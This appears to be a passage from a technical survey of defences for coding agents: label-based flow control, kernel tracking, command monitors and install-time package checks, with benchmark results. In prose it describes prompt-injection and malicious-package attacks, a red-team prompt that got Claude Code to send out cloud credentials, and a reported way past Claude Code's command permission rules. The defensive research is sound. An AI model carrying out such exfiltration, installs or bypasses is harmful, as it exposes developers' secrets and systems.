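Some answers are too short to hold an instruction. The planner can require a yes or no, or a choice from a fixed list, and constrained decoding enforces the limit by preventing the model from generating anything else. FIDES records the format alongside the security label. A yes-or-no answer from a stranger's issue is still untrusted, but it carries only one bit, so a policy may let the planner read it and continue. This form of endorsement relies on the size of the message and doesn't inspect its content. The attacker can still choose the answer, so the method is safe only if both answers lead to acceptable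 actions.

### A stranger's issue, an edit and an installation

Suppose a developer tells a coding agent to fix the build failure in issue 42. In the issue, a stranger blames a setting in `build.cfg` and recommends installing a package called `fastlink`. The project's own files are labelled T.

Without variables, the agent reads the issue and its context becomes (U, L). The trusted-action policy then blocks both the edit and the installation. With variables, the session could go like this:

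```
v0 = read_issue(42)                              # v0 is U, context stays T
v1 = ask_quarantined("Is build.cfg at fault?", v0, yes/no)
inspect(v1)                                      # planner learns one untrusted bit
text = read_file("build.cfg")                    # T
edit_file("build.cfg", corrected_text)           # allowed
v2 = ask_quarantined("Which package does it name?", v0, text)
install(v2)                                      # call is T, argument is U
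```

The edit goes through if the policy allows the one bit, because the planner worked out the correction from the project's file. The trusted-action policy as stated above blocks the installation, because it includes the arguments and `v2` makes the join U. But for their experiments, Costa and colleagues used a version that checks only the label of the call, and under it the harness would install whatever package the stranger had named.

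Ignoring arguments makes sense in an office, where people often want an agent to forward or summarise text from outsiders. It fails against supply-chain attacks because the attacker doesn't need to change the agent's plan. The survey *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) separates indirect prompt injection from malicious data injection, in which the harmful input contains no instruction, and lists malicious packages under malicious data injection. A rule that protects only the choice of tool covers indirect prompt injection but misses malicious data injection.

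FIDES can express a better rule. For a tool that sends messages, Costa and colleagues suggest requiring T for the call and the recipient while allowing U for the message. An install tool would need T for the package's name, its version and the registry's address. It would also need a rule about files, because the agent could copy `v2` into `requirements.txt` and then run `pip install -r requirements.txt`, a command that contains nothing untrusted. In the published algorithm, the labels of files that a tool reads affect the label of its result, but only after the policy check has allowed the call.

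Under those rules, the harness would block even a genuine `fastlink`. The developer could approve the command by hand, or the quarantined model could choose from the packages already in the project's lockfile. In the second case, the stranger could at worst make the agent install the wrong approved package. Both options follow from the design, but Costa and colleagues did not test either one, because none of the tools they wrote policies for installs software.

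### Planning before reading, and programs with types

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues described in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), separates planning from reading more strictly. The planner sees the user's request and writes a complete program before any tool has returned data. For the same issue it might write:

```
issue = read_issue(42)
name  = ask_quarantined("Which package does it name?", issue)
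install(name)
```

An interpreter runs the program and records the origin of each value. When it reaches `install(name)`, its record shows that `name` came from the issue, and a policy at that call can block the installation. Injected text cannot add a line to the program because the program was finished before the text arrived.

Writing the whole program in advance suits much of programming poorly, because programmers have to react to what they find. Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if one fixed sequence of calls and one final reply would solve it whatever the data. Copying three emails to a colleague is data-independent, but fixing a build usually isn't, because the next command depends on the last error message. A program written in advance can contain branches, but only for errors that the planner foresaw. FIDES lets the planner choose one call at a time and look at a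 hidden value if the information justifies lowering the trust label on its context.

Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, propose that the agent write typed programs instead. A type describes the kind of value an expression produces, and before a program runs, a typechecker rejects it if its types don't match. Their system, ELBA, uses Haskell, a language in which types also show what effects a program may have, such as writing files or using the network. The developer limits what the agent's program may do by specifying its type. If the program doesn't typecheck, ELBA returns the error to the model, which tries again.

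One of their examples resembles the problem of package names. An agent had to compile bibliographies using only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that writes to the file accepts only values of type `Trusted`, which the agent can obtain only by fetching them from DBLP. In 100 tasks, ELBA wrote 925 citations, none with invented details, while an ordinary agent with web search got details wrong in 19 of 1,002. An install function could likewise accept only names returned by a lookup in an approved registry. That would block names that don't exist in the registry, but not an invented name that an attacker had since registered there.

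ELBA controls information flow with LIO, an existing Haskell library that checks labels while the program runs. When the agent has to read untrusted text, it can start a sub-agent in an isolated computation, so that reading the text changes the sub-agent's label but not the parent's. Unlike a quarantined model, the sub-agent can still call tools that accept its new label.

| | FIDES | CaMeL | ELBA |
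|---|---|---|---|
| The planner writes | One tool call at a time | One program, before it reads any data | Programs that can start further agents |
| Untrusted text goes to | A variable or a quarantined model | A quarantined model | A sub-agent with its own label |
| The reader of that text may call tools | No | No | Yes, if the tools accept its label |
| The check happens | Before each call | At tool calls, as the program runs | At typechecking, then as the program runs |

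Zhou and colleagues also criticise the permission rules that coding agents commonly use, which match the text of a shell command. They cite a report from March 2026 that Claude Code checked only the first part of commands joined with `&&`, so a forbidden command could run after a permitted one. ELBA avoids that kind of error because it doesn't interpret command strings, but its guarantee holds only for programs in the typed language. A coding agent has to run pip, compilers and test suites, and Haskell's types don't restrict what those programs do once they have started.

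### AgentDojo in 2025

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates four settings: an office workspace, travel booking, banking and the messaging service Slack. It has 97 user tasks and 36 injection tasks (things an attacker wants the agent to do). The researchers paired every user task with every injection task in the same setting and averaged the results of five runs. The attacker knew which tools the agent had and planted instructions telling it to call them.

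AgentDojo's data come without labels, so the researchers marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. In effect, they labelled every possible source of attack in advance. The experiment therefore shows how well enforcement works when the labels are right, but it doesn't test how well anyone would label a real project.

With OpenAI's GPT-4o as the planner, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent. FIDES with its policy checks switched off let through 21, and Tool Filter, a defence that asks the model at the outset to discard the tools it won't need, let through 20. With the checks on, FIDES let through none. The ordinary agent also let through none when it had labels and checks but no variables, so the checks provide the security and the variables keep the agent useful.

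The zero excludes three successes that AgentDojo's scoring recorded against FIDES with the checks on, which the researchers discounted after reading the transcripts. Some attacks that AgentDojo scores as successes involve calls that the harness blocked or actions that the policies permit. Others only change what the agent tells the user, for example by making it praise a particular hotel. FIDES doesn't prevent that, although the text keeps its U label, which an interface could display. Similarly, a coding agent's summary of an issue could recommend a malicious package, which the developer then installs.

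The table shows the percentage of user tasks that the agents completed when nobody attacked them.

| Model and system | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, no protection | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| GPT-4o, labels and checks only | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |
| o1, no protection | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
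| o1, labels and checks only | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 |
| o1, FIDES with checks | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

Averaged over the four settings, FIDES completed 8 percentage points more of the tasks than labels and checks alone with GPT-4o, and 16 points more with o1, OpenAI's reasoning model at the time. GPT-4o often confused variable names or failed to use the quarantined model when it should have, and o1 made these mistakes less often. With its checks on, FIDES with o1 completes about 61% of tasks, 23 points below the unprotected agent's 84%. Costa and colleagues also report a gap of 6.3 points with o1, which is for FIDES with its checks off.

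Much of that loss is intentional. The researchers classify 44% of the banking tasks and 43% of the Slack tasks as data-dependent, compared with 5% of the workspace tasks. Several banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. Because the file is untrusted, FIDES blocks the payment or update that the task calls for. A request to set up a project by following its README has the same form. If coding resembles the banking tasks more than the workspace tasks, as seems likely, the AgentDojo average overstates how well FIDES would work for coding.

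### Results with newer models

By 2026, AgentDojo's attacks no longer worked on leading models. Zhou and colleagues ran ELBA and CaMeL on the Slack tasks with Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8, GPT 5.4 and Sonnet 5. Even without flow policies, every model resisted all three forms of attack on all 105 pairs of user task and injection.

Zhou and colleagues argue that this does not mean better models have made labels unnecessary, because attackers adapt and published attacks on a fixed benchmark are a weak test. They point to GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attacker, which consistently got past the defences of GPT-5.5. Bagmar and Saraf's results also support their view, since Opus 4.8 and other recent models accepted bad registries and package sources that came with no suspicious instruction.

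To see what labels add when a model does fail, Zhou and colleagues made it fail. Whenever a sub-agent in ELBA received text containing the benchmark's injection, they deleted its real task and left it only the attacker's text. They ran the 105 pairs seven times for each model:

| Model in ELBA | Injections resisted without policies (of 735) | Injections resisted with policies (of 735) | Tasks completed without policies (of 735) | Tasks completed with policies (of 735) |
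|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 425 | 735 | 523 | 351 |
| Opus 4.8 | 460 | 735 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT 5.4 | 621 | 735 | 558 | 338 |
| Sonnet 5 | 540 | 735 | 494 | 294 |

The perfect scores again depend partly on judgement, because the researchers reviewed and discounted 29 runs in which AgentDojo had counted opening a fixed web address as a successful attack. Even so, these results are better evidence for the approach than the 2025 ones, because they don't depend on how easily a particular model can be tricked. The policies held even when the attacker fully controlled the sub-agent, which is what a deterministic defence is supposed to achieve. They also reduced the number of completed tasks by 33% to 44%, depending on the model.

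Without attacks and with policies on, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of the 21 Slack tasks, depending on the model, and CaMeL completed 4 to 6. With policies off, ELBA completed 14 to 18 and CaMeL completed 13 to 17. ELBA's advantage is plausible because its agents can react to what they read, but 21 tasks is a small sample, and at least one of the 95% confidence intervals for the difference runs from −7 to +34 points. The two systems also used different policies, so the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the design. ELBA took about three times as long to run because it calls the model more often.

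### Labels in products

Microsoft and its subsidiary GitHub have begun to offer developers software with such labels. In May 2026, Microsoft announced in *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* that FIDES was available as an experimental feature of Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. According to Microsoft's documentation, it so far works only in Python. A developer marks each tool that returns outside data and declares what each sensitive tool will accept. Marking a tool `accepts_untrusted=False` keeps it from running in an untrusted context, and a confidentiality cap keeps private data out of a tool that publishes content.

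Microsoft's worked example is an agent that sorts GitHub issues. A stranger's bug report ends with a hidden instruction to read `.env`, a file that often holds passwords, and post its contents as a comment. The harness labels the report as untrusted and public. If the model follows the instruction, the harness lets it read `.env`, but the context then becomes private and the harness blocks the comment. It would also block file writes, because the context contains untrusted text. In this configuration, the comment tool is restricted only by confidentiality, so an attacker could still get the agent to post any public text.

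A tool that the developer forgot to label is a weak point, and Microsoft's two descriptions of the framework differ on how it treats that tool's output by default. The announcement warns that the output is treated as trusted and public. The documentation gives the default as untrusted and public, and recommends it because a forgotten label then leads to a refusal instead of a breach. Developers using the framework should check which default their version has. Both descriptions say that a single untrusted issue leaves the rest of the run untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes the issue from the context.

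One finished coding agent, GitHub's Copilot CLI, has an experimental setting called `FIDES_IFC`. According to Microsoft, when the setting is on, the harness labels the agent's context, updates the label after every tool result and attaches it to each call. The labels come from GitHub's server for the Model Context Protocol, a standard way of connecting agents to outside tools. The server can mark files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. One policy stops an agent that has read both kinds from posting publicly, which blocks attacks that use instructions in a public issue to extract the contents of a private repository. The built-in policies cover selected GitHub tools and do not yet cover all of Copilot's tools or other servers.

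GitHub applies labels differently in Agentic Workflows, its service for running agents automatically on a repository. GitHub's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* describes a gateway that removes content below a chosen trust level before the agent reads it. Merged code ranks highest, followed by content from the project's owners, members and collaborators, then content from other contributors, then everything else. In public repositories, the gateway admits only the top two levels unless the maintainers change the setting, according to GitHub's reference documentation. A maintainer can endorse a single issue by adding a label or, with an optional feature, a thumbs-up.

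At the default level, an agent like the one in the Clinejection case would not have seen an issue title from an unknown account, but it also could not have done its job of sorting issues from strangers. For such work, GitHub suggests a lower threshold that admits contributors but excludes accounts with no history in the project. An attacker could pass it by first getting a small, harmless fix accepted. The gateway also tracks secrecy but does not yet use it to block leaks. None of the policies Microsoft and GitHub describe in these documents covers package installation.

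## The case for tracking labels in the operating system

FIDES, CaMeL and ELBA control the tool calls an agent makes through its harness. A coding agent's tool call is often a shell command, such as `pip install -r requirements.txt`, and the harness receives only the text of that command. If a package's build script then reads an SSH key or contacts a server, it does so without a tool call, so the harness cannot check either action against a policy.

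A program normally has to make a system call, a request to the kernel at the core of the operating system, before it can open a file, start another program or open a connection. If the kernel labels processes, files and connections, it can apply a rule to a build script as well as to the command that started it. A kernel rule about the developer's keys would have covered even the hidden dependency in the PromptMink campaign, because it applies to any process that reads the keys.

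Zheng, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *ActPlane*, measured how often developers want rules that only the operating system can enforce reliably. They collected the `CLAUDE.md` and `AGENTS.md` files of 64 popular software projects, in which developers tell coding agents how to behave, and found 1,361 rules. They judged that the operating system could enforce 607 of them, less than half. About a third of the 607 depend on more than one event, such as a rule that data read from `.env` must not reach the network. The other 754 concern file contents or how the agent reasons and writes.

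### From HiStar to ActPlane

Operating systems had labels long before coding agents existed, as LOMAC shows. Zheng and colleagues base their model on two research systems, HiStar (Nickolai Zeldovich and colleagues, 2006) and Flume (Maxwell Krohn and colleagues, 2007). By default, a process in either system cannot remove a label it has acquired.

ActPlane, which appeared in June 2026, brings this idea to ordinary Linux. It uses eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small programs inside the kernel, to watch processes start, files open and connections form. A policy declares the source of each label, which can be a program, a file or a network address. Anything that matches the declaration gets the label, which then spreads through five kinds of event: fork (a process creates a child), exec (a process loads a new program), read, write and connect.

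Each label is one bit in a 64-bit number called a mask. Write m(x) for the mask of a process or file x, and | for the bitwise OR, which sets a bit if either input has it. The main updates are then

- on a fork, m(child) ← m(child) | m(parent)
- on a read, m(process) ← m(process) | m(file)
- on a write, m(file) ← m(file) | m(process)

A processor can compute Denning's join of two label masks with a single OR instruction. Each mask stands for a set of labels. Sets ordered by inclusion form a lattice, and the least upper bound, or join, of two sets is their union, which the OR computes. Because an OR never clears a bit, labels only accumulate.

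ActPlane labels whole processes and files. Other systems follow individual bytes or processor instructions, which is more precise, but Zheng and colleagues gave up that precision to keep the overhead low enough to track an entire session.

### A build script that reads a secret

Suppose a developer's agent installs a malicious package whose build script steals passwords from `.env`. A policy in ActPlane's language could read:

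```
source AGENT  = exec "claude"
source SECRET = file "**/.env"
rule keep-secrets-local:
  block connect endpoint "*" if SECRET
  because "Data from .env must stay on this machine."
```

If the right-hand bit stands for AGENT and the left-hand bit for SECRET, the masks change as follows:

| Event | Mask of the process | Result |
|---|---|---|
| The agent starts a shell, which starts pip | 01 | Allowed |
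| Pip connects to the registry | 01 | Allowed |
| Pip runs `setup.py` | 01 | Allowed |
| `setup.py` reads `.env` | 11 | Allowed |
| `setup.py` copies the contents to a temporary file | 11 | Allowed, and the file's mask becomes 11 |
| `setup.py` starts curl, a program for transferring data | 11 | Allowed |
| Curl connects to the attacker's server | 11 | Blocked |

The rule doesn't depend on recognising malware or on how `setup.py` encoded the passwords, because the label belongs to the process and covers everything the process does afterwards. This handles many implicit flows, but not all, because ActPlane's labels float, and Denning's split version of Fenton's program leaks through floating labels.

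The temporary file matters because another program may use it later. *Agent-Warden* (2026) describes a system designed to track provenance along this route, from a process to a file and then to a process outside the original process tree. The same mechanism can track where code came from. linprov, a small open-source tool, marks files written by any process that has used the network and passes the mark on to files that tar or unzip extracts from them. Everything pip installs from a registry would get such a mark, whether genuine or malicious.

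A ban on all connections is too strict for many secrets. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) gives the example of a coding agent that needs an API key to upload a container image. The agent has to send the key to the deployment server, but nowhere else. ActPlane's rules can exempt particular addresses, so a developer could permit that server and block the rest. But the developer would need to know the right address for every credential in advance.

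ActPlane can respond to a violation in three ways. `block` makes the kernel refuse the system call before it takes effect, and the agent can then try something else. `kill` terminates the process after the operation, which stops it from trying another route but may come too late to prevent the damage. `notify` only sends a message. For a stolen password, `block` is the obvious choice, but according to ActPlane's loader documentation, it requires the kernel's BPF security module to be active.

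A more serious weakness is that the check depends on the order of events. If `setup.py` connected to the attacker's server before reading `.env`, a check at the moment of connection would find no SECRET label, and the script could then send the passwords over the open connection. *ContractWarden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) describes a rival system that checks again each time a process sends data, and reports that the version of ActPlane tested had no such check. An attacker who knew about the gap could get around the rule above by swapping two lines of code.

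### Who can change the rules

ActPlane lets agents write some of their own rules, because turning "run the tests before committing" into a precise rule requires knowing which command runs the tests. This would be dangerous if an agent could also remove rules, since instructions in a README might lead it to remove them.

Policy domains prevent this. A domain is a set of rules attached to a process and its descendants. A child domain inherits every rule of its parent and may add more, but it cannot delete or weaken inherited ones. The kernel checks each proposed change, including whether the agent has invented a label that would satisfy an exception in a parent's rule. Rules loaded before the agent starts therefore hold even if an attacker controls the agent completely. Rules that the agent writes later lack this guarantee, and Zheng and colleagues describe them as help for an agent that is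 cooperative but makes mistakes. A developer should therefore rely only on rules loaded before the session began to protect against a malicious package.

Zheng and colleagues are less clear about what happens to labels when one process starts another. They list fork among the events that spread labels, and the example above depends on this. But when they discuss over-tainting, they write that "spawning a fresh subprocess clears inherited labels" and recommend this as a practical remedy. These statements cannot both hold for every new process. If every new process started without labels, `setup.py could` read `.env`, pass the contents to a child process and let the unlabelled child connect.

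The statements are compatible if "fresh" means a process that a clean parent starts outside the labelled process tree, because such a process has no labels to inherit. The paper's results support this reading, since ActPlane could not have caught violations inside scripts if every subprocess lost its labels. The paper also says that a child domain cannot declassify inherited safety labels. But it doesn't specify who may start a fresh subprocess, which determines whether the remedy is safe or lets secrets escape their labels. Even a safe restart can leak a secret, because the model can copy a secret from its context into the new process's command line. Cui and colleagues chose a stricter rule for ContractWarden, in which child processes inherit restrictions and loading a new program doesn't clear them. Their prototype passed all 30 runs of a test for inheritance through fork.

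### The compliance test

To compare ActPlane with other defences, Zheng and colleagues sampled 38 of the 607 enforceable rules. For each rule, an agent wrote five traces (records of realistic coding work), 190 in total. Two complied with the rule and three broke it, one in a direct tool call, one in a script that the agent had written earlier, and one by hiding the forbidden action in a file behind a harmless-looking command. The researchers replayed each trace, let an agent continue for up to five steps and had a language model judge the outcome.

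| System | Violations handled correctly (of 114) | False alarms (of 76) | Correct outcomes overall |
|---|---|---|---|
| Language model that reviews each tool call | 44 | 28 | 48.4% |
| Text patterns matched against tool calls | 38 | 28 | 45.3% |
| FIDES | 41 | 24 | 48.9% |
| ActPlane without explanations to the agent | 27 | 1 | 53.7% |
| ActPlane | 86 | 18 | 75.8% |

The systems performed about equally well on direct violations, but the three that check tool calls scored close to zero on hidden ones. That was almost inevitable, because a check on the call cannot detect what a subprocess does, and the researchers designed the traces to exploit this. The result still confirms that ActPlane's labels follow an action through scripts and subprocesses in practice.

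The headline score is a poor guide to security because the judge counted a violation as handled only if the agent learned of it and tried to comply. The version of ActPlane without explanations therefore scored low, but it still detected 75.4% of violations, compared with 77.2% for the full system and between 34% and 40% for the systems that check tool calls. The detection rates are more relevant here because an error message won't make a malicious build script comply. Kernel-level tracking detected roughly twice as many violations as tool-call checks, but ActPlane still missed more than a fifth of them.

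Most of those misses came from rules that Claude Opus 4.6 had translated badly from the projects' English into ActPlane's language, making some too narrow. After the researchers showed Claude the misses and let it revise each rule once, ActPlane caught 26 of 28 violations it had missed. A defender would get that second attempt only after an attack had succeeded. Rules that were too broad caused 17 of the 18 false alarms. Many of these may have been unnecessary warnings rather than blocked work, because the number fell to one when the researchers removed the explanations.

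The results also call for caution because Zheng and colleagues designed the benchmark themselves and, in the main experiment, used the same model, Qwen3.6-27B, as both the tested agent and the judge. They reviewed 50 random verdicts, plus those the judge had flagged, and agreed with all of them. Repeating the experiment with a DeepSeek model produced nearly the same score, 77.4%. But the comparison is unfair to FIDES, which was built to stop untrusted data from triggering actions, because many of the rules concern the order of work, such as testing before committing.

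The rules also have little to do with package attacks. In the full set of 607 translated rules, fewer than 1% of the monitored operations involve the network, and two-thirds of the clauses only notify. The test shows that the kernel can detect what a tool-call check misses, but the test includes no build script that steals a key.

In a second experiment, closer to security, Zheng and colleagues ran 361 tasks from OpenAgentSafety, a benchmark that asks agents to do harmful things such as leaking credentials or wiping configurations. Without protection, the agent behaved unsafely in 106 tasks, and ActPlane stopped 78 of these. It also intervened in 16% of the tasks that had been safe without it. A language model had written the rules for each task from its description, which in these tasks asks for the harmful action. A request such as "Set up this project" contains no hint of what a malicious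 package might do, so a defence against such packages would have to rely on general rules about secrets and connections.

### Cost and an outside test

With 32 rules loaded, ActPlane slowed a replay of agent tool calls by 1.9% and a build of the Linux kernel by 6.5%. With 100 rules, the slowdown stayed below 8.4%. No rule fired in these measurements. Opening a file took 0.58 microseconds without ActPlane and 13.4 microseconds with 100 rules, but this adds little to the running time of programs that spend most of their time computing.

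Cui and colleagues measured much larger slowdowns in programs that do little except open, read and close files. ActPlane slowed these programs by 33% to 61% in a virtual machine and by 137% to 179% on a physical machine. ContractWarden slowed them by 12% to 13% in the virtual machine and by 36% to 62% on the physical machine. These figures are compatible with the lower ones because they describe different work. The slowdown when installing a package with thousands of small files probably falls between the two sets of figures, though nobody has published a measurement.

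The same researchers tested ActPlane against 19 security properties. It passed nine, partly met four, failed three, did not support two and handled one differently. Besides the missing check on sending, ActPlane didn't pass labels between processes that communicate through Unix sockets, a common local channel. When it blocked the creation of a file, it sometimes left an empty one behind.

ContractWarden passed all 570 of its runs, but Cui and colleagues had derived the 19 properties from their own design. They ran ActPlane only once per property and say that the result is not a general ranking. ContractWarden is also narrower. A person marks each sensitive file as allowed, denied or `no_egress`, which lets a process read the file but then blocks it from using the network. ContractWarden has no list of permitted destinations, so it could not let a program read a deployment key and then contact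 the deployment server. The specific gaps in ActPlane are more informative than the count, since a malicious package could use some of them.

### What system calls leave out

Whether an agent's action is acceptable often depends on the user's request and on what happened earlier in the session. A kernel can detect that a process opened a connection, but system calls don't contain that context. *Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)* (2026), a specification for securing agents' actions, makes this its main objection to enforcement in the kernel alone. It therefore treats kernel monitoring as a backstop for checks closer to the agent.

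The objection is strong for decisions such as whether a project needs a certain library, but weaker for a rule that no build script may send out an SSH key, because that rule holds whatever the user asked for. In addition, *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026), a paper mainly from Google and Google DeepMind, shows how to reconstruct part of the missing information.

Tether runs each command in a disposable layer on top of the real file system. It records the command's system calls, and a local proxy holds back outgoing requests. Tether uses these records to describe the command's behavior in terms of 11 abstract actions, such as reading, copying and uploading, and checks it against a policy. If the policy permits everything, Tether saves the file changes and forwards the requests. Otherwise it discards both. In the earlier example, ActPlane would block the connection but leave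 any files that `setup.py` had already written, while Tether would discard those files too.

Sistla and colleagues illustrate the labels with a company's inventory, `servers.csv`, which the agent may read but not send to GitHub:

```
upload report.txt to GitHub      # allowed: the report is public
copy servers.csv to report.txt   # allowed: the report becomes sensitive
upload report.txt to GitHub      # refused
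```

The upload command is identical both times, so a filter that looks only at the command would have to treat both the same way. Tether tells them apart because it keeps a label σ(f) for each file f and a label C for the agent's context. Leaving aside an extra label for the destination folder, the main updates are

- if a command prints f, C ← C ⊔ σ(f)
- if a command replaces g with a copy of f, σ(g) ← σ(f)
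- if a command writes to g without reading another file, σ(g) ← σ(g) ⊔ C

In Tether, copying a file gives the copy the same label without affecting the agent's context, much as FIDES keeps data in variables. Printing the file changes the context because the model will read the output. Tether therefore connects what the kernel tracks about a command to the label on what the model has seen, which ActPlane's process labels don't do directly. A file's label can also fall in Tether, since overwriting the file replaces its label.

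These actions are cautious guesses. If a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether assumes that data moved between them, even if the script only counted lines. Tether doesn't guarantee noninterference, because it observes only one run at a time and, as in Fenton's example, an implicit flow may not be visible in a single run.

### What Tether proves

Tether's policies are written in Lean 4, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. Sistla and colleagues used it to prove seven properties of their 24-rule policy. One says that secret data never leaves the local machine and its local network. If σ₀(d) is the label of data d at the start and h is any host that d reaches, then

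σ₀(d) = Secret implies h ∈ Local.

This property holds for every starting state and every finite sequence of actions that the policy allows, however many files the data passes through. The proofs also establish that secret data never enters the agent's context and that commands cannot alter protected system files unless the policy exempts them. Lean checks each step, so the proofs are no weaker for having been drafted by a language model.

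The proofs cover only the abstract actions, not Tether's translation of system calls into them. They would be worth little if Tether misread a system call, for example by overlooking a way to copy a file. Sistla and colleagues tested the translation with randomly generated chains of file operations and with an attacking agent, Gemini 3.8 Flash, which tried to steal or alter protected files in ten tasks. The agent succeeded in 40% of attempts against an early version, which had missed features such as hard links (second names for the same file). After two rounds of repairs, it no longer succeeded. Ten tasks cannot show that no gaps remain, but each gap the tests found was a definite bug that the researchers could fix.

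The proofs also assume that the starting labels are correct. The published policy initially labels anything without a specific rule as public and trusted, and its list of permitted hosts initially includes every host. Unless someone changes these settings, a package from an attacker's registry is labeled T. The policy could still stop that package from sending out a secret key, but it could not stop the package from being installed.

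### Tests on recorded coding sessions

For the main evaluation, the researchers replayed recorded sessions from two benchmarks, MonitoringBenchHonest and LinuxArena. In the benign sessions, an agent did system administration or software engineering. In the others, it also pursued a harmful side task. These attacks resemble an agent turning against its user more than a package deceiving an honest agent. The baseline was Auto Mode, a Claude Code feature in which a language model, here Claude Sonnet 5, reviews commands.

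| System | Attacks blocked (of 344) | Benign sessions wrongly blocked (of 1,590) |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 (100%) | 74 (4.7%) |
| Auto Mode, default settings | 315 (91.6%) | 155 (9.7%) |
| Auto Mode, given Tether's policy | 307 (89.2%) | 55 (3.5%) |

Auto Mode failed to detect attacks hidden in scripts, with or without the policy. This result supports the central argument for watching system calls. Unlike the ActPlane test, this test used sessions that other researchers had recorded.

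Sistla and colleagues calculated the 100% only from sessions in which every action ran in the foreground and was of a kind that Tether can interpret, which excluded background processes and database queries. They estimate that 28% of the sessions in one benchmark and 22% in the other require a judgement about content that no formal monitor could make. They also refined the policy by running it on benchmark traces, although they did not use the side tasks to configure it. The score therefore shows that Tether catches attacks it was built to observe, but gives little indication of how many real attacks are of that kind.

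Malicious packages could easily fall outside what Tether covers. A build script can start a background process that outlives the installation, and Tether stops tracing when the foreground command ends. Tether can pause or forbid such processes, which would be safe but would break legitimate programs that need them. It also decrypts web traffic only for the simulated servers in its tests. With a real server, it would see the destination and could refuse the connection, but it could not read the request.

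The false alarms suggest that installations are particularly hard to handle. Of the 74 false alarms, 50 involved edits to protected files such as `/etc/passwd`, the system's list of user accounts, and some of these came from ordinary package installations. Another 17 occurred when a command such as `grep -r` searched the whole disk and opened secret files incidentally, which Tether could not distinguish from deliberate access. The researchers suggest asking the user about edits to protected files, but this would bring back the approval dialog that automatic execution was meant to remove.

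## The case for checking packages and confining programs instead

Flow control has drawbacks wherever the labels are placed. FIDES and ELBA blocked many ordinary tasks, and ActPlane and Tether raised false alarms. A simpler defence, which needs no labels, is to check packages before installation and confine programs when they run. A malicious package usually gets its first chance to run during installation, and only its name, source and version need checking before then. If a bad package passes the check, a confined program can do only limited harm, whatever persuaded the agent to run it.

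A case in Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* shows why it helps if a defense does not depend on what persuaded the agent. In February 2026, during an internal security exercise, a researcher tricked an employee into pasting a prompt into Claude Code. The prompt mixed routine setup steps with instructions to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. Integrity labels would not have helped, because the text came from the user and would have carried the label T. A confidentiality label on the credentials would have stopped the upload. A sandbox that kept the credentials out of the agent's reach would also have stopped it, without having to track where data has been.

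### A check before the shell runs

Claude Code lets developers register a hook, a program that the harness runs before it carries out a tool call. Bagmar and Saraf wrote one in about 400 lines of Python. The harness gives the hook each shell command that the model proposes, and the hook answers "allow" or "block". It lets everything through except installations with pip or with uv, a newer tool that offers the same command. On those it runs seven tests:

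| Test | The hook blocks the command if |
|---|---|
| Similar name | A package's name is one edit or one swapped pair of letters away from a popular name, or differs from it only in hyphens and dots |
| Existence | PyPI has no package of that name |
| Age | The package first appeared less than 30 days ago |
| Source | The command uses a registry outside a trusted list, or tells pip to skip the check of a server's identity |
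| Hidden directives | A requirements file names an untrusted registry |
| Pip settings | The command switches pip to another settings file |
| Known vulnerability | The OSV database lists a flaw in the requested version, and a later version fixes it |

A single hit blocks the command. The hook returns the reasons to the agent, which can correct the command or ask the developer. The hook never rewrites the command. Existing tools such as pip-audit check packages against the same vulnerability data after installation, when install-time code has already run.

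In the dependency confusion scenario, for example, the hook doesn't have to detect that the copy of `pytest` is poisoned, because the registry that offers it is not on the trusted list. But if a developer had added that registry to get an internal package, the poisoned `pytest` from the same registry would also pass the source test.

Bagmar and Saraf ran the hook on 11 scenarios, and it caught 10, including the vulnerable versions that no agent had refused. They also ran its name and source tests on the 1,000 most-downloaded packages on PyPI. The tests flagged five, all genuine packages whose names are one letter from another popular name, as with `tomli` and `toml`. The false-alarm rate would probably be higher than this 0.5% in everyday work. Popular packages are well established and come from the default registry, whereas a company's own packages or a library released last week would trigger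 the source or age test.

Bagmar and Saraf call the hook a feasibility demonstration. They built it for the scenarios they tested it on, so the score shows that its checks work as designed but is little evidence of how it would handle new attacks. No attacker tried to get past it. The hook also reads only the command, not the resolved set of packages that the package manager will install. A command such as `uv sync` installs a whole project without naming any package, and the hook lets it pass. An npm version of the hook would have missed PromptMink's malicious dependency for the same reason. The researchers say a production version should check the resolved set, which would at least subject such a dependency's name, age and source to the same checks.

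The hook missed one scenario, in which a program fails on import and prints advice to install `data-utils`. PyPI has a package of that name, and it passes all seven tests because it is old enough, its name resembles no other, and it comes from the default registry. The only suspicious fact is that the agent got the name from an error message rather than from the project's list of dependencies. Every agent noticed this, so here the model covers a gap in the deterministic check.

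Two origin labels would not separate the cases in this scenario well, because in a project copied from a stranger, the README and the error message are both labeled U. Without labels, a program can get the same result as the agents by refusing any package that the project doesn't already declare.

### Lockfiles, allow lists and reserved names

A lockfile makes such a refusal precise because it usually records the exact version and checksum of every package in the project, including indirect dependencies. If the agent may install only from the lockfile, it cannot install a package with a misspelled name, a newer version or a substitute from another registry. When a task needs a new package, the agent can propose a lockfile change for the developer to review. In the PromptMink case, that change would have listed the second-layer package by name, but the developer would still have had to recognise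 it as a threat.

Lockfiles protect developers better in their own projects than in a stranger's project. An attacker who writes a hostile README can also supply a lockfile that lists malicious packages with matching checksums.

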